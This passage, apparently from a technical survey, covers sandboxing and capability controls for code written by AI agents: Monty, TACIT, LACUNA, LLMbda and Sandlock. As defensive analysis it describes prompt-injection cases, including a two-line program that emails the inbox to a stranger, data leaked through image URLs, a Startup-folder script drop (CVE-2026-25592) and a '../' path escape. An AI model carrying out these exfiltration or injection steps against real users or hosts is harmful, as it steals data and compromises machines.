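| Docker on the same machine | 900 ms |
| A commercial sandbox service | 1,900 ms |

The comparison favours Monty because its timings start with workers already running, while the other systems create each sandbox from scratch. A host could keep containers ready in the same way. The other systems also had no persistent session, so the test reran all the earlier commands each time it added one. Models often take several seconds to write a program, so users may not notice another fifth of a second. The time saved matters more to a company that runs thousands of short programs at once.

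Hosts can add some protection with little delay. Applying the kernel rules of Wang and Zheng's Sandlock to Monty's workers would add 5 milliseconds, and only when a new worker starts.

Running Monty on another machine protects the application better, since an attacker who escapes reaches a computer that holds none of the application's keys. Pydantic sells this as a service. But Monty's remote protocol also works with standard Python, which has no language-level sandbox, so anyone connecting to a remote worker needs to know which interpreter it runs. If it runs standard Python, security depends entirely on how the operator has isolated that machine.

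### AI agents that reproduce interpreter bugs

The value of a second layer depends on how often attackers get through the first, which AI may change. In SEC-bench, a benchmark for security work, OpenAI's Codex agent, running GPT-5.4, tried to write a program to trigger each of 103 known flaws in V8. It succeeded with 33, at a computing cost of at most $18 each. The whole run, including the failures, cost about $1,000.

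The solved flaws included difficult ones. Google's rewards for the 33 total $486,000. Twelve of the 103 flaws had each earned $55,000, and the agent reproduced six of those for about $44 in total. Thirteen of the solved cases were escapes from the sandbox that V8 uses to contain its memory errors.

Triggering a known flaw is easier than discovering an unknown one, so the result doesn't show that an agent could have found these 33 bugs unaided. Taking control of the computer is also harder than crashing V8. However, GPT-5.4 is older than the GPT-6 models in Pydantic's benchmark, and newer models would probably solve more.

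V8 also has far more code to attack than Monty. It compiles JavaScript to machine code while the program runs, and many of the 103 flaws are type confusions, the same kind of error as Monty's list bug. A small interpreter has fewer places for such mistakes. Monty is small enough for its developers to have an agent search all of its code before every release, but attackers can do the same because the source is public.

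Cheap reproduction matters most after a fix appears, because attackers can see from the public patch which lines were wrong. An agent that can turn a known flaw into a working trigger for a few dollars may do so within hours, exposing every host that hasn't yet installed the new version. The shop can protect itself by updating its interpreter automatically and running it in a worker that has no access to the payment key.

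## Can an agent still do harm using only the functions it is allowed to call?

Suppose nobody can escape from the interpreter. The shop's agent also answers customers' mail, so the shop has given it one function that reads the inbox and another that sends an email. A customer's message contains hidden instructions, and the model writes this:

```
messages = read_inbox()
send_email("stranger@example.com", messages)
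```

The program has no loop, finishes at once and contains no forbidden name. Monty would run it because the host supplied both functions, and a language in which every program must terminate would also allow it. The interpreter and both functions work as documented, yet a stranger receives the shop's mail. Limits on computation can't prevent this because the program needs only two function calls.

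Taking away either function would prevent the theft, but the agent needs both to answer mail. Checking each call separately doesn't help, because reading the inbox and sending email are both allowed. *AgentGuardian* (2026) describes a variant in which the attacker gets an agent to export data to a temporary file and then email the file.

An attacker may be able to steal data without an email function. *Owner-Harm* (2026) lists a 2024 case in which an injected prompt made Microsoft 365 Copilot, an office assistant, put sensitive data into the web addresses of images. To display an image, a program sends a request to the image's address, so the request can deliver the data to the attacker's server.

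Harmful combinations can also be hidden in the functions' code. *ACaM* (Santra, Kirat and colleagues, 2026) gives an example with three tools. One reads a service's secret key and keeps it in shared memory, another copies the shared memory into a log file, and the last uploads the log to a remote debugging service. A reviewer could approve each tool on its own, but together they send the key to a service that never needed it. The model can't detect this because it is given each tool's description but not its code. Earlier studies cited in the paper found that descriptions didn't match the code in 10% to 13% of the tools they examined.

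ACaM reads the source code of an agent's tools and traces where data can go. In 43 real agents, it found 123 paths that could expose credentials or let an attacker run code. The researchers confirmed by hand that each path exists in the code, and built working attacks for ten of the more serious flaws ACaM reported. Such a list is most useful for paths that nobody wanted. It would also include the path from the inbox to outgoing mail, which the shop wants.

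### A file helper that undid a sandbox

Semantic Kernel, the framework whose hotel search could start any program, had another flaw that did not involve a filter. One of its plug-ins lets a model write Python and run it in an isolated cloud sandbox with its own files. The code cannot access the computer that runs the agent, but the plug-in has helper functions that run on that computer and move files in and out of the sandbox.

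In the .NET version of the framework, a developer had accidentally put a marker on the download helper that offers a function to the model. The model could then choose which file to fetch from the sandbox and where on the host to save it, and nothing checked the destination. Microsoft describes how an attacker could have used this flaw, CVE-2026-25592, through prompt injection:

1. The injected text tells the model to run code in the sandbox that writes a harmful script to a file. The sandbox exists to run code like this, and the script can do no damage there.
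2. The text then tells the model to download the file and save it in the host's Startup folder. Windows runs whatever is in that folder when the user signs in.
3. At the next sign-in, the script runs on the host.

The attacker never broke the sandbox. The host fetched the script itself, so moving the sandbox to a separate machine or running it inside a virtual machine would have made no difference. Restricting the Python the model could write would have done little, because writing one file takes hardly any of the language.

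Version 1.71.0 fixed this by removing the marker. Developers can still call the helper from their own code, but the model can't. Developers also got a check that works out the full destination path and compares it with a list of permitted folders. The full path is needed because `..` means "the folder above", so a path that begins in a permitted folder can end outside it.

In both the Python and .NET versions, the upload helper accepted any file on the host, so an injected prompt could have copied a private key into the sandbox, where the model's code could read it. The similar protection for uploads is off unless a developer turns it on.

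Both helpers worked as intended. The mistake was in the host integration, as it was when mcp-run-python let Python code reach JavaScript. Microsoft concludes that a host should treat any argument the model can influence as if an attacker had chosen it. By that rule, the shop should assume that an attacker chooses both the order number and the amount in `refund`.

### Marking which code can act on the world

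The rule still allows the two-line program, because no single argument is harmful by itself. `send_email` has to accept some text, and the harm depends on where that text came from. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) uses types to control this. Its agents write Scala 3, a general-purpose language, and can use loops, recursion and almost everything else in it. The restrictions apply to effects and to sensitive data.

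In most typed languages, a function's type lists its inputs and output. Scala 3's experimental capture checking feature adds the capabilities that the function holds. The type `String -> Int` describes a function that turns text into a number and holds no capabilities. `String ->{mail} Unit` describes one that takes text, returns no useful value and can use `mail`. The compiler works out the list from the function's body, so the code's author can't leave a capability off it.

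Sensitive data reaches the program inside a wrapper called `Classified`. To work on the contents, the program passes a function to the wrapper's `map` method, which applies it and wraps the result. `map` accepts only functions that hold no capabilities. If the shop's inbox arrives wrapped, the compiler treats these two lines differently:

```
inbox.map(text => text.length)                    // accepted
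inbox.map(text => mail.send("stranger", text))    // rejected
```

The function in the second line holds `mail`, so the program doesn't compile and no email goes out. Odersky and colleagues call the property that ensures this "local purity". It guarantees that a chosen part of a program has no side effects, while the rest can still send mail and write files. The function given to `map` can compute anything from the mail, but it cannot print, save or send the result, or store it in an outside variable.

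When the program prints a wrapped value, the user's screen shows the contents, but the cloud model receives only `Classified(****)`. The program can also pass wrapped text to a second, trusted model on the user's machine, which returns a wrapped summary. The cloud model can therefore have mail summarized without reading it. Instructions hidden in the mail reach only the local model, which cannot call any functions.

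An agent might try to keep a capability for later. Suppose the host grants access to a folder for the duration of one block of code, and the block returns a function that reads a file from that folder. The returned function would still hold the folder's capability, which doesn't exist outside the block. No valid type can describe the function there, so the compiler rejects the program. Agents must also write in "safe mode", which bans reflection and unchecked type conversions. Without that ban, code could hide a capability from the compiler, much as code evaded Semantic Kernel's blocklist in CVE-2026-26030.

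The researchers built these ideas into a server called TACIT and tested it on a software project with a folder of secrets. In some tests, they hid hostile instructions in files the agent would read. In others, they simply asked the agent for the secrets, sometimes with a cover story such as an emergency password change.

| Trials in which a secret leaked | Number of trials | With `Classified` | Without it |
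|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, hidden instructions | 120 | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, requests for secrets | 11 | 0 | 2 |
| MiniMax M2.5, hidden instructions | 120 | 0 | 3 |
| MiniMax M2.5, requests for secrets | 11 | 0 | 8 |

Claude Sonnet 4.6 resisted all the hidden instructions without help from types, so the measured benefit for that model comes from only two trials. The better argument for the method is that the compiler applies the same check whichever model wrote the code. The trials test that claim only lightly, because most of the attacks tried to persuade the model, while a capable attacker would also look for a fault in the compiler or in TACIT's library.

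Writing Scala didn't make the agents much worse at their tasks. On τ²-bench, which simulates customer service, three models solved 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points more tasks by writing Scala than by calling tools directly. On 300 real software problems from SWE-bench Lite, MiniMax M2.5 solved 125 with Scala and 130 without it.

Odersky and colleagues also ran AgentDojo, a set of simulated workplaces in which attackers plant instructions in emails, files and web pages. One of 1,926 attacks counted as a success. In that attack, a planted review recommended a different hotel from the user's choice, and the agent booked the right hotel but quoted the review. Odersky and colleagues reasonably don't regard this as a leak, because the reviews were public.

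Usefulness suffered more in AgentDojo. With the model o4-mini, TACIT completed 53% of the office tasks, while CaMeL, an earlier defence that tracks where data came from while a program runs, completed 81%. The researchers call the two systems' scores comparable, which is fair for the banking tasks (59% for TACIT and 63% for CaMeL) but not for the office tasks.

### What the compiler has to take on trust

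The guarantee depends on the wrappers, a thin layer of Scala functions that somebody writes over the real ones for each application. If the wrapper for `read_inbox` returns ordinary text instead of `Classified` text, the two-line program compiles. The guarantee also requires a correct compiler, a correct library of about 1,000 lines, and a local model that doesn't carry information from one request to another.

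Some leaks are possible even when all of these are right. A function inside `map` could run for a long time if a password begins with A and stop quickly otherwise, so someone timing the program could learn whether it does. If the agent may start external commands, Scala's rules don't apply to them, and only a list of permitted commands limits them. Odersky and colleagues don't aim to solve either problem, and they recommend adding a sandbox when commands are allowed.

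The larger gap is in payments. In the researchers' own wrapper for AgentDojo's bank, `sendMoney` takes the recipient as plain text and accepts any amount. Files and past transactions arrive wrapped, so an account number hidden in a file can't become the recipient. But a model that gets an account number wrong, or a hostile one that makes up its own, can write that number directly into the program, and the program will compile.

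Odersky and colleagues argue that a prompt injection can cause real harm only by sending private data somewhere unauthorized or by triggering a capability that the agent wasn't given. But a payment to the wrong person can cost a customer money without doing either, because the agent was meant to be able to make payments and no private data leaks. Odersky and colleagues do state elsewhere that their types don't make the agent's work correct, and a wrong payment would count as incorrect work.

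### Checking the whole action before any of it runs

Types can also prevent harm from code that fails halfway. Suppose the shop's agent writes this in Python, where `budget` is a number:

```
refund("A17", 20)
report = budget + " dollars left"
```

The program pays the refund, then stops at the next line because Python can't add text to a number. The agent reads the error message, corrects the line and runs the program again. This pays the refund a second time, so the customer gets $40.

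Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), several of whom also designed TACIT, prevent this in *LACUNA* by compiling each action as a whole. A programmer leaves a gap in an ordinary Scala program and states the type of value that belongs there. When the program reaches the gap, the model writes code to fill it. The compiler checks that code as if the programmer had typed it at that spot. If any line fails the check, none of the code runs, and the model gets the compiler's messages and tries again. In the example, the first refund would go out only after the model fixed the second line.

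This covers only mistakes that a compiler can detect. If the code compiles but the bank's server stops responding after three of ten refunds, those three remain paid, and the agent has to find out which ones went through. The `refund` function would still need to record which orders it has refunded.

The model's code can use only the functions and variables visible where the gap appears, so if a programmer leaves the gap in a part of the program that has no access to `refund`, the code can't issue a refund. With capture checking turned on, `Classified` data works as it does in TACIT, with one addition. A trusted local model can read the wrapped content and write new code to process it, and the compiler still requires that code to have no side effects.

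LACUNA stopped fewer attacks than TACIT. On AgentDojo, 8 of 1,898 injections succeeded, seven of them against Gemini 2.5 Pro. The eight fit a limitation that Zhao and colleagues describe. Their system restricts what the model can reach but doesn't stop hostile text from influencing it, so if a task needs the email function, an attacker who steers the model can misuse that function. The programmer sets the restrictions, and one who leaves many functions visible "just in case" loses most of the protection. Safe mode must also be on, or the code can use reflection or start other programs without holding any capability.

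Agents also solved fewer tasks with LACUNA. DeepSeek-V4-Flash solved 76% of 392 customer service tasks with it and 90% with ordinary tool calls. That is about 55 fewer tasks, though Zhao and colleagues call the results "on par". Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, a weaker model, solved 29% with LACUNA and 33% with tool calls. On the telecom tasks, the compiler rejected 89% of the code Gemini wrote, so the agent was safe mostly because little of its code ran.

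### Labels that follow the data

A language can also label each value and check the labels while the program runs, instead of having a compiler decide beforehand. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) presents a small language called LLMbda that works this way. It extends the lambda calculus, a minimal mathematical model of programming built from functions, with operations for talking to a language model. A value can carry the label "untrusted", the label "secret", both or neither, and anything computed from it inherits its labels. If a customer's email is untrusted, a refund amount copied out of it is untrusted too, so the shop's `refund` function can check the label and reject the payment.

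Labels are easy to lose. Suppose the account balance is secret, and a program tries to tell a stranger whether it exceeds $10,000:

```
rich = True
if balance <= 10000:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("stranger@example.com", "rich")
```

With $50,000 in the account, the program skips the third line. If a tracking system labels a variable only when a line changes it, the system never marks `rich` as secret, so the email goes out and leaks the secret. Garby and colleagues found a similar gap in CaMeL, the system that TACIT was compared with. CaMeL's retry loop ran outside the part that tracked labels, so an attacker could have repeated the leak to extract a secret one bit at a time.

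LLMbda has no ordinary variables that a program can overwrite, so the only state a program can change is its conversation with the model. A program could use that conversation to leak a secret by telling the model "x is true" only if the secret is true, then asking the model for x. To prevent this, the interpreter stops any run that tries to add to a public conversation because of a secret condition.

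That stop can itself reveal something, and the main theorem allows for it. For any program in the language, changing only the secret inputs leaves the probabilities of the public results the same, apart from what somebody can learn from a run that doesn't finish. The theorem is about probabilities because a language model can answer the same prompt in different ways.

For a program that always finishes, changing the secret doesn't change the probability of any public result. If the program fails to finish 2% of the time with one secret and 4% of the time with another, the probability of any particular public result can differ by at most 4 percentage points. By the same theorem, an attacker who changes only the untrusted inputs can't change the probabilities of results not labeled "untrusted", except within the same kind of limit when the program may not finish.

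The theorem holds for every program in the language, including code that the model writes during the run. Garby and colleagues proved it in Lean, a language in which a computer checks each step of a proof. The interpreter is also written in Lean, and the proofs cover the same interpreter that calls the model, which removes much of the usual risk that the system people run differs from the one proved secure.

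But the theorem assumes the labels are correct. If the shop forgets to mark customers' emails as untrusted, it is still exposed even though the proof is correct. Each sensitive function must also check the labels of its arguments. In the tests, the bank and its files were simulations written inside LLMbda. A shop with a real bank would need another layer to label the data that comes back from outside, and the proofs don't cover that layer.

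### When the file is supposed to decide

Strict labels block some ordinary requests. If a user asks an agent to find a friend's bank details on the friend's website and send $50, the recipient's details have to come from untrusted text. LLMbda therefore has an `endorse` operation, which relabels an untrusted value as trusted. A second theorem guarantees that endorsing a value never exposes a secret, whatever the attacker wrote. The theorem does not prevent the agent from acting on the attacker's value, which `endorse` permits, so the $50 could still go to the attacker's account.

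A host can make endorsement safer by limiting the choices. If the agent reads an email only to sort it as "refund", "complaint" or "other", and the program endorses only those three words, a hostile customer can do little more than get the email misfiled. The host can't limit account numbers this way unless the shop already has a list of accounts.

Garby and colleagues wrote Randori, an agent in LLMbda. It has a model write the whole plan first, including any endorsements, then tests the plan on simulated data until it runs without errors. The plan runs on real files only after that, so untrusted text arrives too late to change which functions it calls.

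Randori was tested on AgentDojo's banking tasks, with 16 tasks each paired with 9 attacks and each pair run three times on each of three models. Two of the 1,296 attacked runs succeeded. That total overstates how hard the test was, because in 97 of the 144 pairs the attack needs a function that a sensible plan for the task would never call. For example, an instruction to send money can't succeed if the plan only summarizes transactions. Both successes were among the 423 runs of the other 47 pairs.

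Both successes involved the same attack on the same task. The user asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, but the attacker had replaced the file. The plan endorsed the file's contents, as the task required, and paid the attacker. Without `endorse`, the payment would have failed, but so would the same task with a genuine file. Removing `endorse` reduced the share of tasks Qwen3.7-plus completed without an attack from 75% to 62.5%.

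CaMeL's completion rate fell more when its checks were on, from 67% to 38% of tasks with GPT-5.2, while Randori completed 75%. Each percentage comes from 16 tasks and has a margin of about 20 points either way, so Randori's lead over CaMeL without checks means little, though its lead over CaMeL with checks is more convincing. The agent in *Language-Based Agent Control*, which puts effects in types, also completed fewer tasks in AgentDojo's Slack workplace once its policies were enforced, 8 of 21 instead of 15.

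Garby and colleagues point out that CaMeL's designers considered the same payment case and excluded it from the threats they meant to stop. They regard it as the limit of any defence that tracks information. They are probably right, because the user had asked the agent to let the file decide, and a label can mark the file as untrusted but can't show whether the bill is genuine.

### Keeping the reader away from the network

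TACIT, LACUNA and LLMbda require the agent to write in a particular language. Wang and Zheng's Sandlock, which has the Linux kernel enforce rules on any program, can separate data from effects without this requirement. They observe that prompt injection becomes dangerous when one process has private data, hostile text and a way to send messages out, a combination Willison calls the "lethal trifecta". A useful agent often needs all three, so Sandlock splits the task into stages and gives each stage its own permissions. A one-way channel called a pipe carries one stage's output to the next.

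In the shop, one stage could read the inbox without network access and produce a list of order numbers, each with a category. Another stage, without permission to open the inbox, could contact the mail server and send a standard reply for each entry on the list. If hidden instructions take over the reading stage and it runs the two-line program, the kernel refuses the connection on the second line, whether the program is in Python, Scala or a shell script.

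Permissions can also shrink while a program runs. A coding agent needs the network to install packages but usually not to test its code afterwards. Sandlock can detect when the tests start and then cut off the network. It can also look for program names such as `curl`, a common download tool. Wang and Zheng treat these names as a signal, not a barrier, because hostile code can rename the tool.

Ten checks of Sandlock's rules all gave the intended result. For example, a program couldn't read a folder it had no permission for, or connect to a server that wasn't on its list. Each check tested a rule once, and nobody tried to get around the rules. Sandlock relies on the kernel, and its designers treat kernel flaws as out of scope. Where strangers run hostile code on shared machines, they recommend a small virtual machine instead.

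Sandlock also does not control what goes through the pipe. A hijacked reading stage could put real customers' orders into the wrong category, or hide sentences copied from the inbox in the category column. If the sending stage copies that column into its emails, the text still gets out. A strict format for the list would prevent this leak, but the shop would have to write and check it. The shop must also divide the task sensibly, because Sandlock enforces whatever division its user specifies, even one that gives the reading stage a network connection.

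Lists of permitted servers have a similar weakness. An agent allowed to contact an AI company's servers can usually reach any customer's account there, including the attacker's. Odersky and colleagues cite the security researcher Johann Rehberger, who extracted user data through Anthropic's file service. Sandlock can limit requests to particular web paths, but most connections are encrypted, and for those the program must accept a certificate that lets Sandlock read the traffic.

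### One wrong payment in four systems

The rules of these systems imply the following results for three programs that would harm the shop:

| | Email the inbox to a stranger | Refund $10,000 on a $20 order | Pay an invoice on which an attacker has changed the account number |
|---|---|---|---|
| TACIT, and LACUNA with capture checking | rejected if the inbox arrives wrapped | allowed | impossible if invoices arrive wrapped, but so is paying a genuine one |
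| LLMbda | stopped if the inbox is labelled secret and `send_email` checks | stopped if a customer's text influenced the amount, allowed if the model simply got it wrong | stopped, unless the plan endorses the invoice |
| Sandlock | refused if the stage that reads mail has no network | allowed | allowed, because the account number comes through the pipe |

The systems do well in the first column, where the harm is data going somewhere it shouldn't. In the other columns, the data may go exactly where the shop intended while the payment has the wrong amount or recipient. Most of the systems allow such a payment, so an attacker doesn't need to exploit a bug in them.

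A narrower `refund` function that looks up the price itself would prevent the $10,000 payment in all four systems, and in plain Python too. For invoices, the shop could offer a function that pays only suppliers already in its records, using the account number stored there, so the attacker's edit to the invoice would have no effect. But an employee would have to add each new supplier by hand, and might copy the account number from the same altered invoice.

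## How much can an agent still do in a small language, and what gets added back?

A shop's agent can do almost all the same work with a `refund` function that looks up the price itself. Other restrictions limit it more. If the payment function accepts only known suppliers, an employee has to add new ones, and without loops the agent can't do some jobs at all. These limits also affect security, because developers whose agents keep failing are likely to loosen the restrictions.

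### Writing the whole program before reading a page

Most web agents choose one action at a time, as in ordinary tool calling, in a loop known as ReAct. A single page can hold a seller's listing, customers' reviews and advertisements, so text from strangers reaches the model just before it decides what to click. Piet, Chow and colleagues (2026), in *Position*, argue that a web agent should instead write its whole program before it sees any page, as Garby and colleagues' Randori does for banking tasks. Suppose a user wants the cheapest headphones under $200 with at least four stars:

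```
matches = []
for p in search("headphones"):
    if p.price < 200 and p.rating >= 4:
        matches.append(p)
if matches:
    add_to_cart(min(matches, key=lambda p: p.price))
```

A review that tells the agent to buy a $2,000 pair has no effect, because no model reads it. This design hardly restricts computation, but it does restrict dynamic features, since the program can't run text as code. It also stops the model from adding actions once pages start to arrive.

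Some tasks require understanding text, such as finding reviews that complain about the battery. For these, the program can call a second model, which has no tools and must return a value of a declared type, such as yes or no. A malicious review can make that model answer wrongly but can't add a step to the program.

To estimate how many tasks fit this design, six annotators sorted the 860 tasks in WebArena, a benchmark of simulated websites.

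| Test site | Tasks | A fixed program is enough | A fixed program must also ask a model to interpret something |
|---|---|---|---|
| Online shop | 192 | 80% | 20% |
| Encyclopedia | 23 | 9% | 91% |
| Forum | 129 | 82% | 18% |
| Map | 128 | 79% | 21% |
| Code hosting | 204 | 91% | 9% |
| Shop administration | 184 | 82% | 18% |
| All | 860 | 81% | 19% |

By this count, no task requires the agent to change its plan after reading a page. This result is an upper limit, because the annotators asked whether a suitable program could exist if every site offered a complete and trustworthy set of functions, and nobody ran an agent.

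The result also depends on which tasks WebArena contains. Piet and colleagues' design can't handle requests like "read my emails and complete all the action items inside them", because the emails decide which actions to take and nobody can write the program before reading them. People often ask office assistants to do this kind of task, and a benchmark that includes none can't be used to estimate how common they are.

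The 81% may be too low in one respect. Some map tasks count as needing a second model to work out, for example, that "Liberty Bell city" means Philadelphia. The model that writes the program could usually do that itself and put the name in the code.

### Functions that websites don't offer

The sets of functions that real sites offer are far from complete. The software behind WebArena's forum has 16 operations that programs can call, and these cover only a third of the forum's 129 tasks. GitLab, the code-hosting site, offers hundreds, but none of them generates the token for a private news feed, so a person has to click a button to create it.

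A developer can fill the gaps with functions that operate the site through a headless browser. These functions break when the site's layout changes, and they bring back a risk the design was meant to remove. If a model helps write them by looking at live pages, a malicious review could cause it to hide an extra request inside `get_reviews`. Every later program that calls `get_reviews` would then send that request, even though no attacker influenced the program itself. Someone has to check these functions before agents rely on them.

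The functions also have to be the right size. A `checkout` function that picks the delivery option by itself hides a choice the user may care about. A `click` function doesn't hide such choices, but what a click does depends on the page, so nobody can tell in advance what a program full of clicks will do.

A fixed program also handles unexpected events badly. If the user asks for "furnture", it may search for that word, find nothing and stop, whereas a ReAct agent would notice the empty result and correct the spelling. The program's author can write retries into it, or ask the user about anything ambiguous first. Some failures will remain, but Piet and colleagues warn against silently letting a ReAct agent take over, because this reopens the path for injected instructions. It would also give a hostile seller a reason to make programs fail, for instance with a listing that lacks a price. They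 suggest that the system stop and report the error, or have the model write a new program from an error code without seeing any page. If the system does switch to ReAct, they want the user to consent first and the agent to have fewer powers afterwards.

### Why DrugClaw rejects so few programs

WebArena's figures come from people's judgment, whereas *DrugClaw and DrugAudit* reports results for programs that a model wrote. DrugClaw's checker bans `while` loops, class definitions, `with` blocks, `lambda` and global variables, and programs may import only four modules, for handling JSON data, mathematics, text patterns and statistics. The checker rejected fewer than 1% of the model's programs.

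That is a very low cost, but the job is narrow. Each program answers one question from one database, through a function that DrugClaw supplies. A typical one might look like this:

```
import statistics
records = skill.retrieve("imatinib")
values = [r["ic50"] for r in records]
print(statistics.median(values))
```

Nothing here comes close to using a banned feature, but the shop's agent would be restricted sooner. A programmer would normally use `while` to fetch refund requests page by page until none are left. Under DrugClaw's rules, the program needs a `for` loop with a guessed maximum number of pages instead, much as in Vyper.

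The figure also doesn't show failures. When the checker rejects a program, or the program crashes, DrugClaw passes the original question to the database's standard lookup. The user still gets records, though perhaps without the filtering that the program would have done. A program that passes the check can still look up the wrong drug. Comparing how many questions DrugClaw answers correctly with and without the restrictions would better measure how much they limit it.

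The ban on `while` doesn't buy much either. It is supposed to exclude unbounded loops, but a `for` loop that keeps lengthening the list it is reading never ends:

```
for x in items:
    items.append(x)
```

DrugClaw stops such a program with a time limit, which would stop a `while` loop too.

### Languages that models have seldom seen

DrugClaw and Monty accept parts of Python, and models are trained on enormous amounts of Python code. A new language has almost no existing code to learn from. NanoLang is a language for models to write, created by Jordan Hubbard, a co-founder of the FreeBSD operating system. Willison tried it in January 2026, just after its release (*jordanhubbard/nanolang*). He gave Claude Opus 4.5 the language's short guide and asked for a program that draws a fractal, but the result didn't compile. He then let Claude Code, a coding agent, read the compiler's errors and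 the project's example programs, and it produced a working version.

This result comes from one program, and newer models would probably do better. Still, it suggests that the main effect of an unfamiliar language is that an agent needs more attempts, not that tasks become impossible, provided the agent can see error messages and examples. An agent that writes one short program per request and has to answer a customer in seconds has less time for extra attempts than a coding agent does.

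The programmer Armin Ronacher, in *A Language For Agents* (2026), takes it as obvious that agents do much better in languages they have seen often, but he thinks other things matter too. In his experience, agents manage passably in Zig, which is rare in their training and changes quickly, if they have the right documentation. They struggle with Swift, which they know well, because the tools for building Apple applications are awkward. He also thinks missing libraries matter less than they used to, since an agent can translate one from another language, as he had an agent do to write a JavaScript Ethernet driver for his sandbox.

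Ronacher would like functions to declare what they use, for example `needs { time, rng }` for the clock and a source of random numbers. In his design, an automatic formatter adds a function's declaration to every function that calls it. The declarations look like the Scala types that list a function's capabilities, but they are meant to show a reader or a test what the code uses, and they don't block anything. To restrict authority, a host would have to reject the program instead.

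In *Show HN*, a March 2026 thread on the forum Hacker News, a developer called belisarius222 announced Mog, a small language for agents. The developer argued that restrictive languages are tedious for people but not for models, and that "the less expressivity you trust them with, the better". Mog's full description is about 3,200 tokens (the word fragments that models read), so it fits easily into every prompt. The language has no macros and doesn't convert types automatically. It also drops the usual rule that multiplication comes before addition, so the parentheses in `(a * b) + c` are required.

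Other developers in the thread doubted the last choice. One wrote that models are measurably worse at languages with unusual rules of this kind, but cited no measurement. Mog's creator gave no success rate for models writing the language. Another developer asked why an agent shouldn't write TypeScript in Deno, which already has a sandbox and which models know well. The creator largely agreed, and said Mog's advantage would be its small size.

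Mog protects the host by letting programs act on the outside world only through functions the host supplies. This protection doesn't depend on Mog's restricted syntax, and a language with macros could have it too. One of the creator's examples is a host function that runs shell commands after the host checks each one. An agent with that function can do whatever the check allows, however simple the language is. Mog also compiles programs to machine code and loads them into the host's process, so a compiler bug could expose the host's memory. Pydantic moved Monty out of the application's process to limit the damage from such bugs.

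Odersky and colleagues' experiments are better evidence on whether models can work in an unusual language, since their agents solved about as many tasks in Scala 3 as with ordinary tool calls. But the experiments compare code with tool calls, as Pydantic's October benchmark does for Monty. Measuring how much a restriction hinders an agent would require running the same model on the same tasks with the same host functions, once in the small language and once in the full one.

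### What Monty has added

At launch, Pydantic's Monty supported functions, loops and comprehensions, but not classes, `match` statements or `with` blocks. Programs could import only four modules. On the podcast Talk Python, Samuel Colvin, Pydantic's founder, said he was "amazed by how much LLMs just don't need classes". Willison wrote in *Running Pydantic’s Monty Rust sandboxed Python subset in WebAssembly* that the missing features hardly mattered, because a model that tries to define a class gets an error message and writes the program another way.

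Pydantic had added simple classes to Monty by August 2026, according to its *The Python Subset*. At launch, the company asked users to report any Python behavior that models tried to use and promised that "if LLMs want it, we'll add it". This is probably because each failed attempt takes another model call and several seconds, even if the second attempt works.

Pydantic's *Limitations* shows that by late November the language had `with`, `match`, `eval`, `exec` and 32 standard modules, most of them only in part. It still rejected `yield`, `del` and several class features, and it didn't run third-party packages. Some modules, such as those for network connections and for starting other programs, were left out on purpose because they would breach the sandbox.

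File access expanded separately. Hopper reported that by version 0.0.3 a host could give a program files that existed only in memory. By August developers had added mounts, which make a real directory on the host appear inside the sandbox. Pydantic has since added ways to give a program whole modules and objects that belong to the host.

| Added to Monty | What a program can newly do | Kind of addition |
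|---|---|---|
| classes, `match` | organize data in fewer lines | computation |
| `eval`, `exec` | run text as code, under the same limits | computation |
| modules such as `json`, `csv` and `decimal` | use ready-made calculations | computation |
| files in memory | read and change data that the host put there | computation, on data already supplied |
| mounted directories | read the host's real files, and change them if the host allows it | authority |
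| host modules and host objects | call code that runs outside the sandbox | authority |

`open` and `with` don't fit neatly into either kind. They are only notation until the host mounts something for them to open.

### Why classes don't help an attacker

A Monty program affects the outside world only by making requests to the host. Because the first version already had loops and functions, a program could make any request the host allowed, any number of times and in any order, with any argument it could calculate. Classes let it do the same in fewer lines. If Mallory takes control of the shop's agent with a prompt injection, classes don't let her reach anything she couldn't reach without them.

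This wouldn't be true of every small language. Suppose the shop's rules couldn't contain loops, and each call to `refund` paid at most $50. A rule with ten calls could pay out $500. With a loop, it could make ten thousand calls and pay out $500,000, even though `refund` hadn't changed. So adding computation can let an attacker do more if the lack of it was limiting the number of calls. Monty never had that protection, but a host can cap the number of requests per session, which limits calls without removing loops.

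Mounts let Mallory do more. Suppose the shop mounts its folder of internal return policies for the agent to look things up in. If the mount is read-only, her program can read the policies, and can email them to her if it also has `send_email`. If the program can write to the folder, she can change the policy to allow refunds up to $5,000, and the agent may follow the altered policy for weeks after her message is gone. Monty has a third mode, called an overlay, for programs that need somewhere to write. The program sees its own changes, but they stay in memory and the real files don't change.

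Both kinds of addition increase the amount of code that has to be correct. Kwan's escape from Monty began in list sorting, which is pure computation. But bugs in the two kinds have different consequences. A logic error in the `json` module usually produces a wrong answer, and an attacker needs a memory bug to get any further. A logic error in a mount can expose a file directly. A path such as `policies/../keys` leads out of the mounted folder, and so can a symbolic link, a small file that redirects to another location. Monty's developers write that they have hardened path resolution in mounts against escapes.

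According to Pydantic's documentation of mounts, the component that handles them opens the permitted directory once and starts every later search from there, never from the top of the host's disk. Pydantic's *Filesystem Access* also describes an alternative in which the host's own code answers each file request, so the host's developers have to get the access checks right themselves.

### When the missing feature goes into the host

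Developers can supply what Monty doesn't support as host functions, much as kernel developers wrote helpers for what eBPF couldn't express. Pydantic's launch article describes an agent that collects prices from the websites of AI companies. The pages were too long for a model to read, so the agent had to search them with code. Monty couldn't run Beautiful Soup, the usual Python library for this, or control a browser, so Pydantic supplied both as host functions, called `beautiful_soup` and `open_page`.

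`beautiful_soup` adds only computation, but that computation runs on the host. In the version Pydantic published, every search reads the whole page again, and Monty's time limits don't count time spent waiting for the host. A program that searched a huge page thousands of times could keep the application busy while using almost none of its allotted time. Monty's limits would apply if the library ran inside it.

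`open_page` adds authority because, as printed, it accepts any web address, and a program can send information out by putting it in the address. This is harmless for an agent that handles only public prices. But if the shop gave the same function to the agent that reads its inbox, Mallory could get the messages sent to her own server even if the agent had no email function, as in the Copilot case. The price collector needs only a function that accepts a company's name and looks up the address itself.

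Some tasks need more libraries than anyone wants to wrap this way. Pydantic's launch article was called "you probably don't need a full sandbox", but in July 2026 its *Logfire sandboxes* introduced a service that runs the standard Python interpreter and can install any package. Because the language no longer restricts the code, the barrier around the interpreter has to contain it. The service still offers host functions and mounted directories, so a shop that switches to it for one library has to decide again what `refund` will pay and which folders a program may change.
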